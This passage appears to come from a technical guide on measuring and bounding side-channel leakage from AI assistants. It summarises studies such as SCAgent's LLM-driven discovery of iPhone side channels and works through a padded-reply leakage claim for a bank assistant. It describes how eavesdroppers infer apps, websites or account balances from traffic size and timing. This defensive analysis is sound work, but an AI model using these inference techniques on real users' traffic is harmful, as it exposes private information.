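Recording real traffic closes most of the gap between the test environment and the live service, provided the developer records packets after the last proxy. Similarly, *FreeSBee* argues that checking a program's source code is useful only under strong assumptions about the compiler, while checking the compiled program also covers leaks that the compiler introduced. To avoid recording real customers, an agent's developer can use invented accounts on the live service.

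*Rethinking Side-Channel Analysis* (May 2026) describes SCAgent, a system that automatically searches for unlisted channels. It looks for ways an ordinary iPhone app with no special permissions could infer which other app or website the user has open. A language model reads system documentation and proposes things the app could measure. A verifier rejects a proposal if it conflicts with the documentation, needs access the app doesn't have, or fails to reach twice the accuracy of random guessing in a small trial. The reasons for rejection guide the next round of proposals.

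Of 80 proposals, 39 passed. One was the amount of free disk space, which was enough by itself to identify the open app from 100 options 93.1% of the time. SCAgent then built attacks with and without the channels already known from earlier studies:

| Channels available to the attack | Correct app | Correct website |
|---|---|---|
| All | 98.1% | 96.7% |
| Only those that earlier iPhone studies had not reported | 95.0% | 90.1% |

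A developer who closed every known channel and tested each one would have reduced the attack's accuracy by only three to seven percentage points. The main tests used an old version of Apple's software, but with all channels available, the attack still identified 96.5% of websites on iOS 26.4.2.

A model could search for an agent's side channels in a similar way, by reading the documentation for the agent's framework, network library and tools. However, *Rethinking Side-Channel Analysis* tests the method only on iPhones. Finding no channels also wouldn't show that none exist, because the result depends on which model does the search. The search found 39 channels with Gemini 3 Pro but only 19 with Grok 3.

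In the same experiments, a trained attacker's success depended heavily on the training method. Using identical channels, an older kind of classifier identified 52.0% of websites and a newer one identified 96.7%. A developer who had tested with only the older classifier would have greatly underestimated the leak.

Counting the possible outcomes gives an upper limit on leakage only if the count is complete. If replies can have only two sizes and two release times, each reply leaks at most two bits. That limit no longer holds if release times also vary by a few milliseconds with the length of the text.

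A proof covers inputs that nobody tested, such as the one PIN in 10,000, but only within its model of the system. HACL*'s proof covered its source code, but the compiler then undid the protection. The theorem by Garby and colleagues does not cover reply times or lengths. CaMeL's retry-loop leak came from code outside its tracked interpreter.

*Smooth, Integrated Proofs of Cryptographic Constant Time for Nondeterministic Programs and Compilers* (2025) extends constant-time proofs to machine instructions. The developer no longer has to trust the compiler, but still has to trust the Coq proof checker and a description of what each instruction leaks on one type of processor.

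Combining methods is useful when their assumptions differ. *FreeSBee* combines measured running times with an analysis that calculates the shortest and longest times a program could take. The measurements cover only the tested inputs. The analysis covers every input but depends on a model of the processor, which the measurements don't need.

### A claim for the bank assistant

Suppose the assistant sends every reply as one 2,048-byte message, 15 seconds after the request. If a reply isn't ready, the server sends it at 30 seconds, or sends an error message of the same size if it still isn't ready then. The developer could make this claim:

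| Part | Content |
|---|---|
| System | Version 4.2 of the assistant, with a fixed model version, tool list and proxy configuration |
| Observer | An eavesdropper who records the time, size and direction of packets between the user and the assistant's server, with timing noise of at least 50 milliseconds (standard deviation), and who can't see other connections or influence the prompt |
| Secret | Whether the balance is below 1,000 |
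| Public information | When the user sends requests, and what they contain |
| Bound | After 30 replies, an observer who started with even odds guesses correctly at most 54% of the time |
| Evidence | A test of every message length, simulated-clock tests, and recorded traffic from 3,000 live runs on each side of 1,000 |
| Confidence | At least 90%, for accounts and requests like those in the live runs |

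A test can check message size without statistics by trying every message length that fits in 2,048 bytes and verifying that the padded size is always the same. The recorded traffic then confirms that no proxy changes that size.

The developer does need to estimate the rate of late replies. Suppose none of the 6,000 live runs missed the 15-second release. To be 95% confident about both groups at once, the developer uses 97.5% for each, which raises the upper bound on the rate from 3/n to 3.7/n, where n is the number of runs in each group. That bound is 0.12%. If the runs are independent, 30 replies can add at most 30 × 0.12%, or about 3.7%, to the distance between what the observer sees at low and at healthy balances.

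The exact release time adds a little more to the distance. Suppose the developer records the traffic next to the server, where the noise is only 5 milliseconds, and an equivalence test shows that the two groups' average release times differ by less than 1 millisecond. If the observer's noise follows a bell curve and the balance shifts only the average, a 1-millisecond difference adds 4.4% over 30 replies. The total distance is then 8.1%, and the observer's best possible accuracy is one half plus half of that, or about 54%. The confidence is at least 90% because the late-reply estimate and the equivalence test can each be wrong 5% of the time.

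The bound depends heavily on where the observer is. An observer close enough to the server to face 5 milliseconds of noise instead of 50 could be right up to 71% of the time from release times alone. To make the same claim about that observer, the developer would have to show that the difference is below about 0.1 milliseconds. The 6,000 runs can't show that, and they already take 25 hours when run one after another.

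The live runs also can't rule out a rare exception like the PIN shortcut. To rule one out, the developer could add a code review or an information-flow check showing that the code for padding and releasing replies never uses the balance. If anything in the claim's first row changes, including the model version, the claim lapses and the developer has to repeat the live runs.

Finally, the claim treats the user's requests as public, but a real user's requests may depend on earlier answers. Someone who learns that they can't afford a holiday may ask three more questions about money, and an eavesdropper who counts those questions may learn something about the answer.
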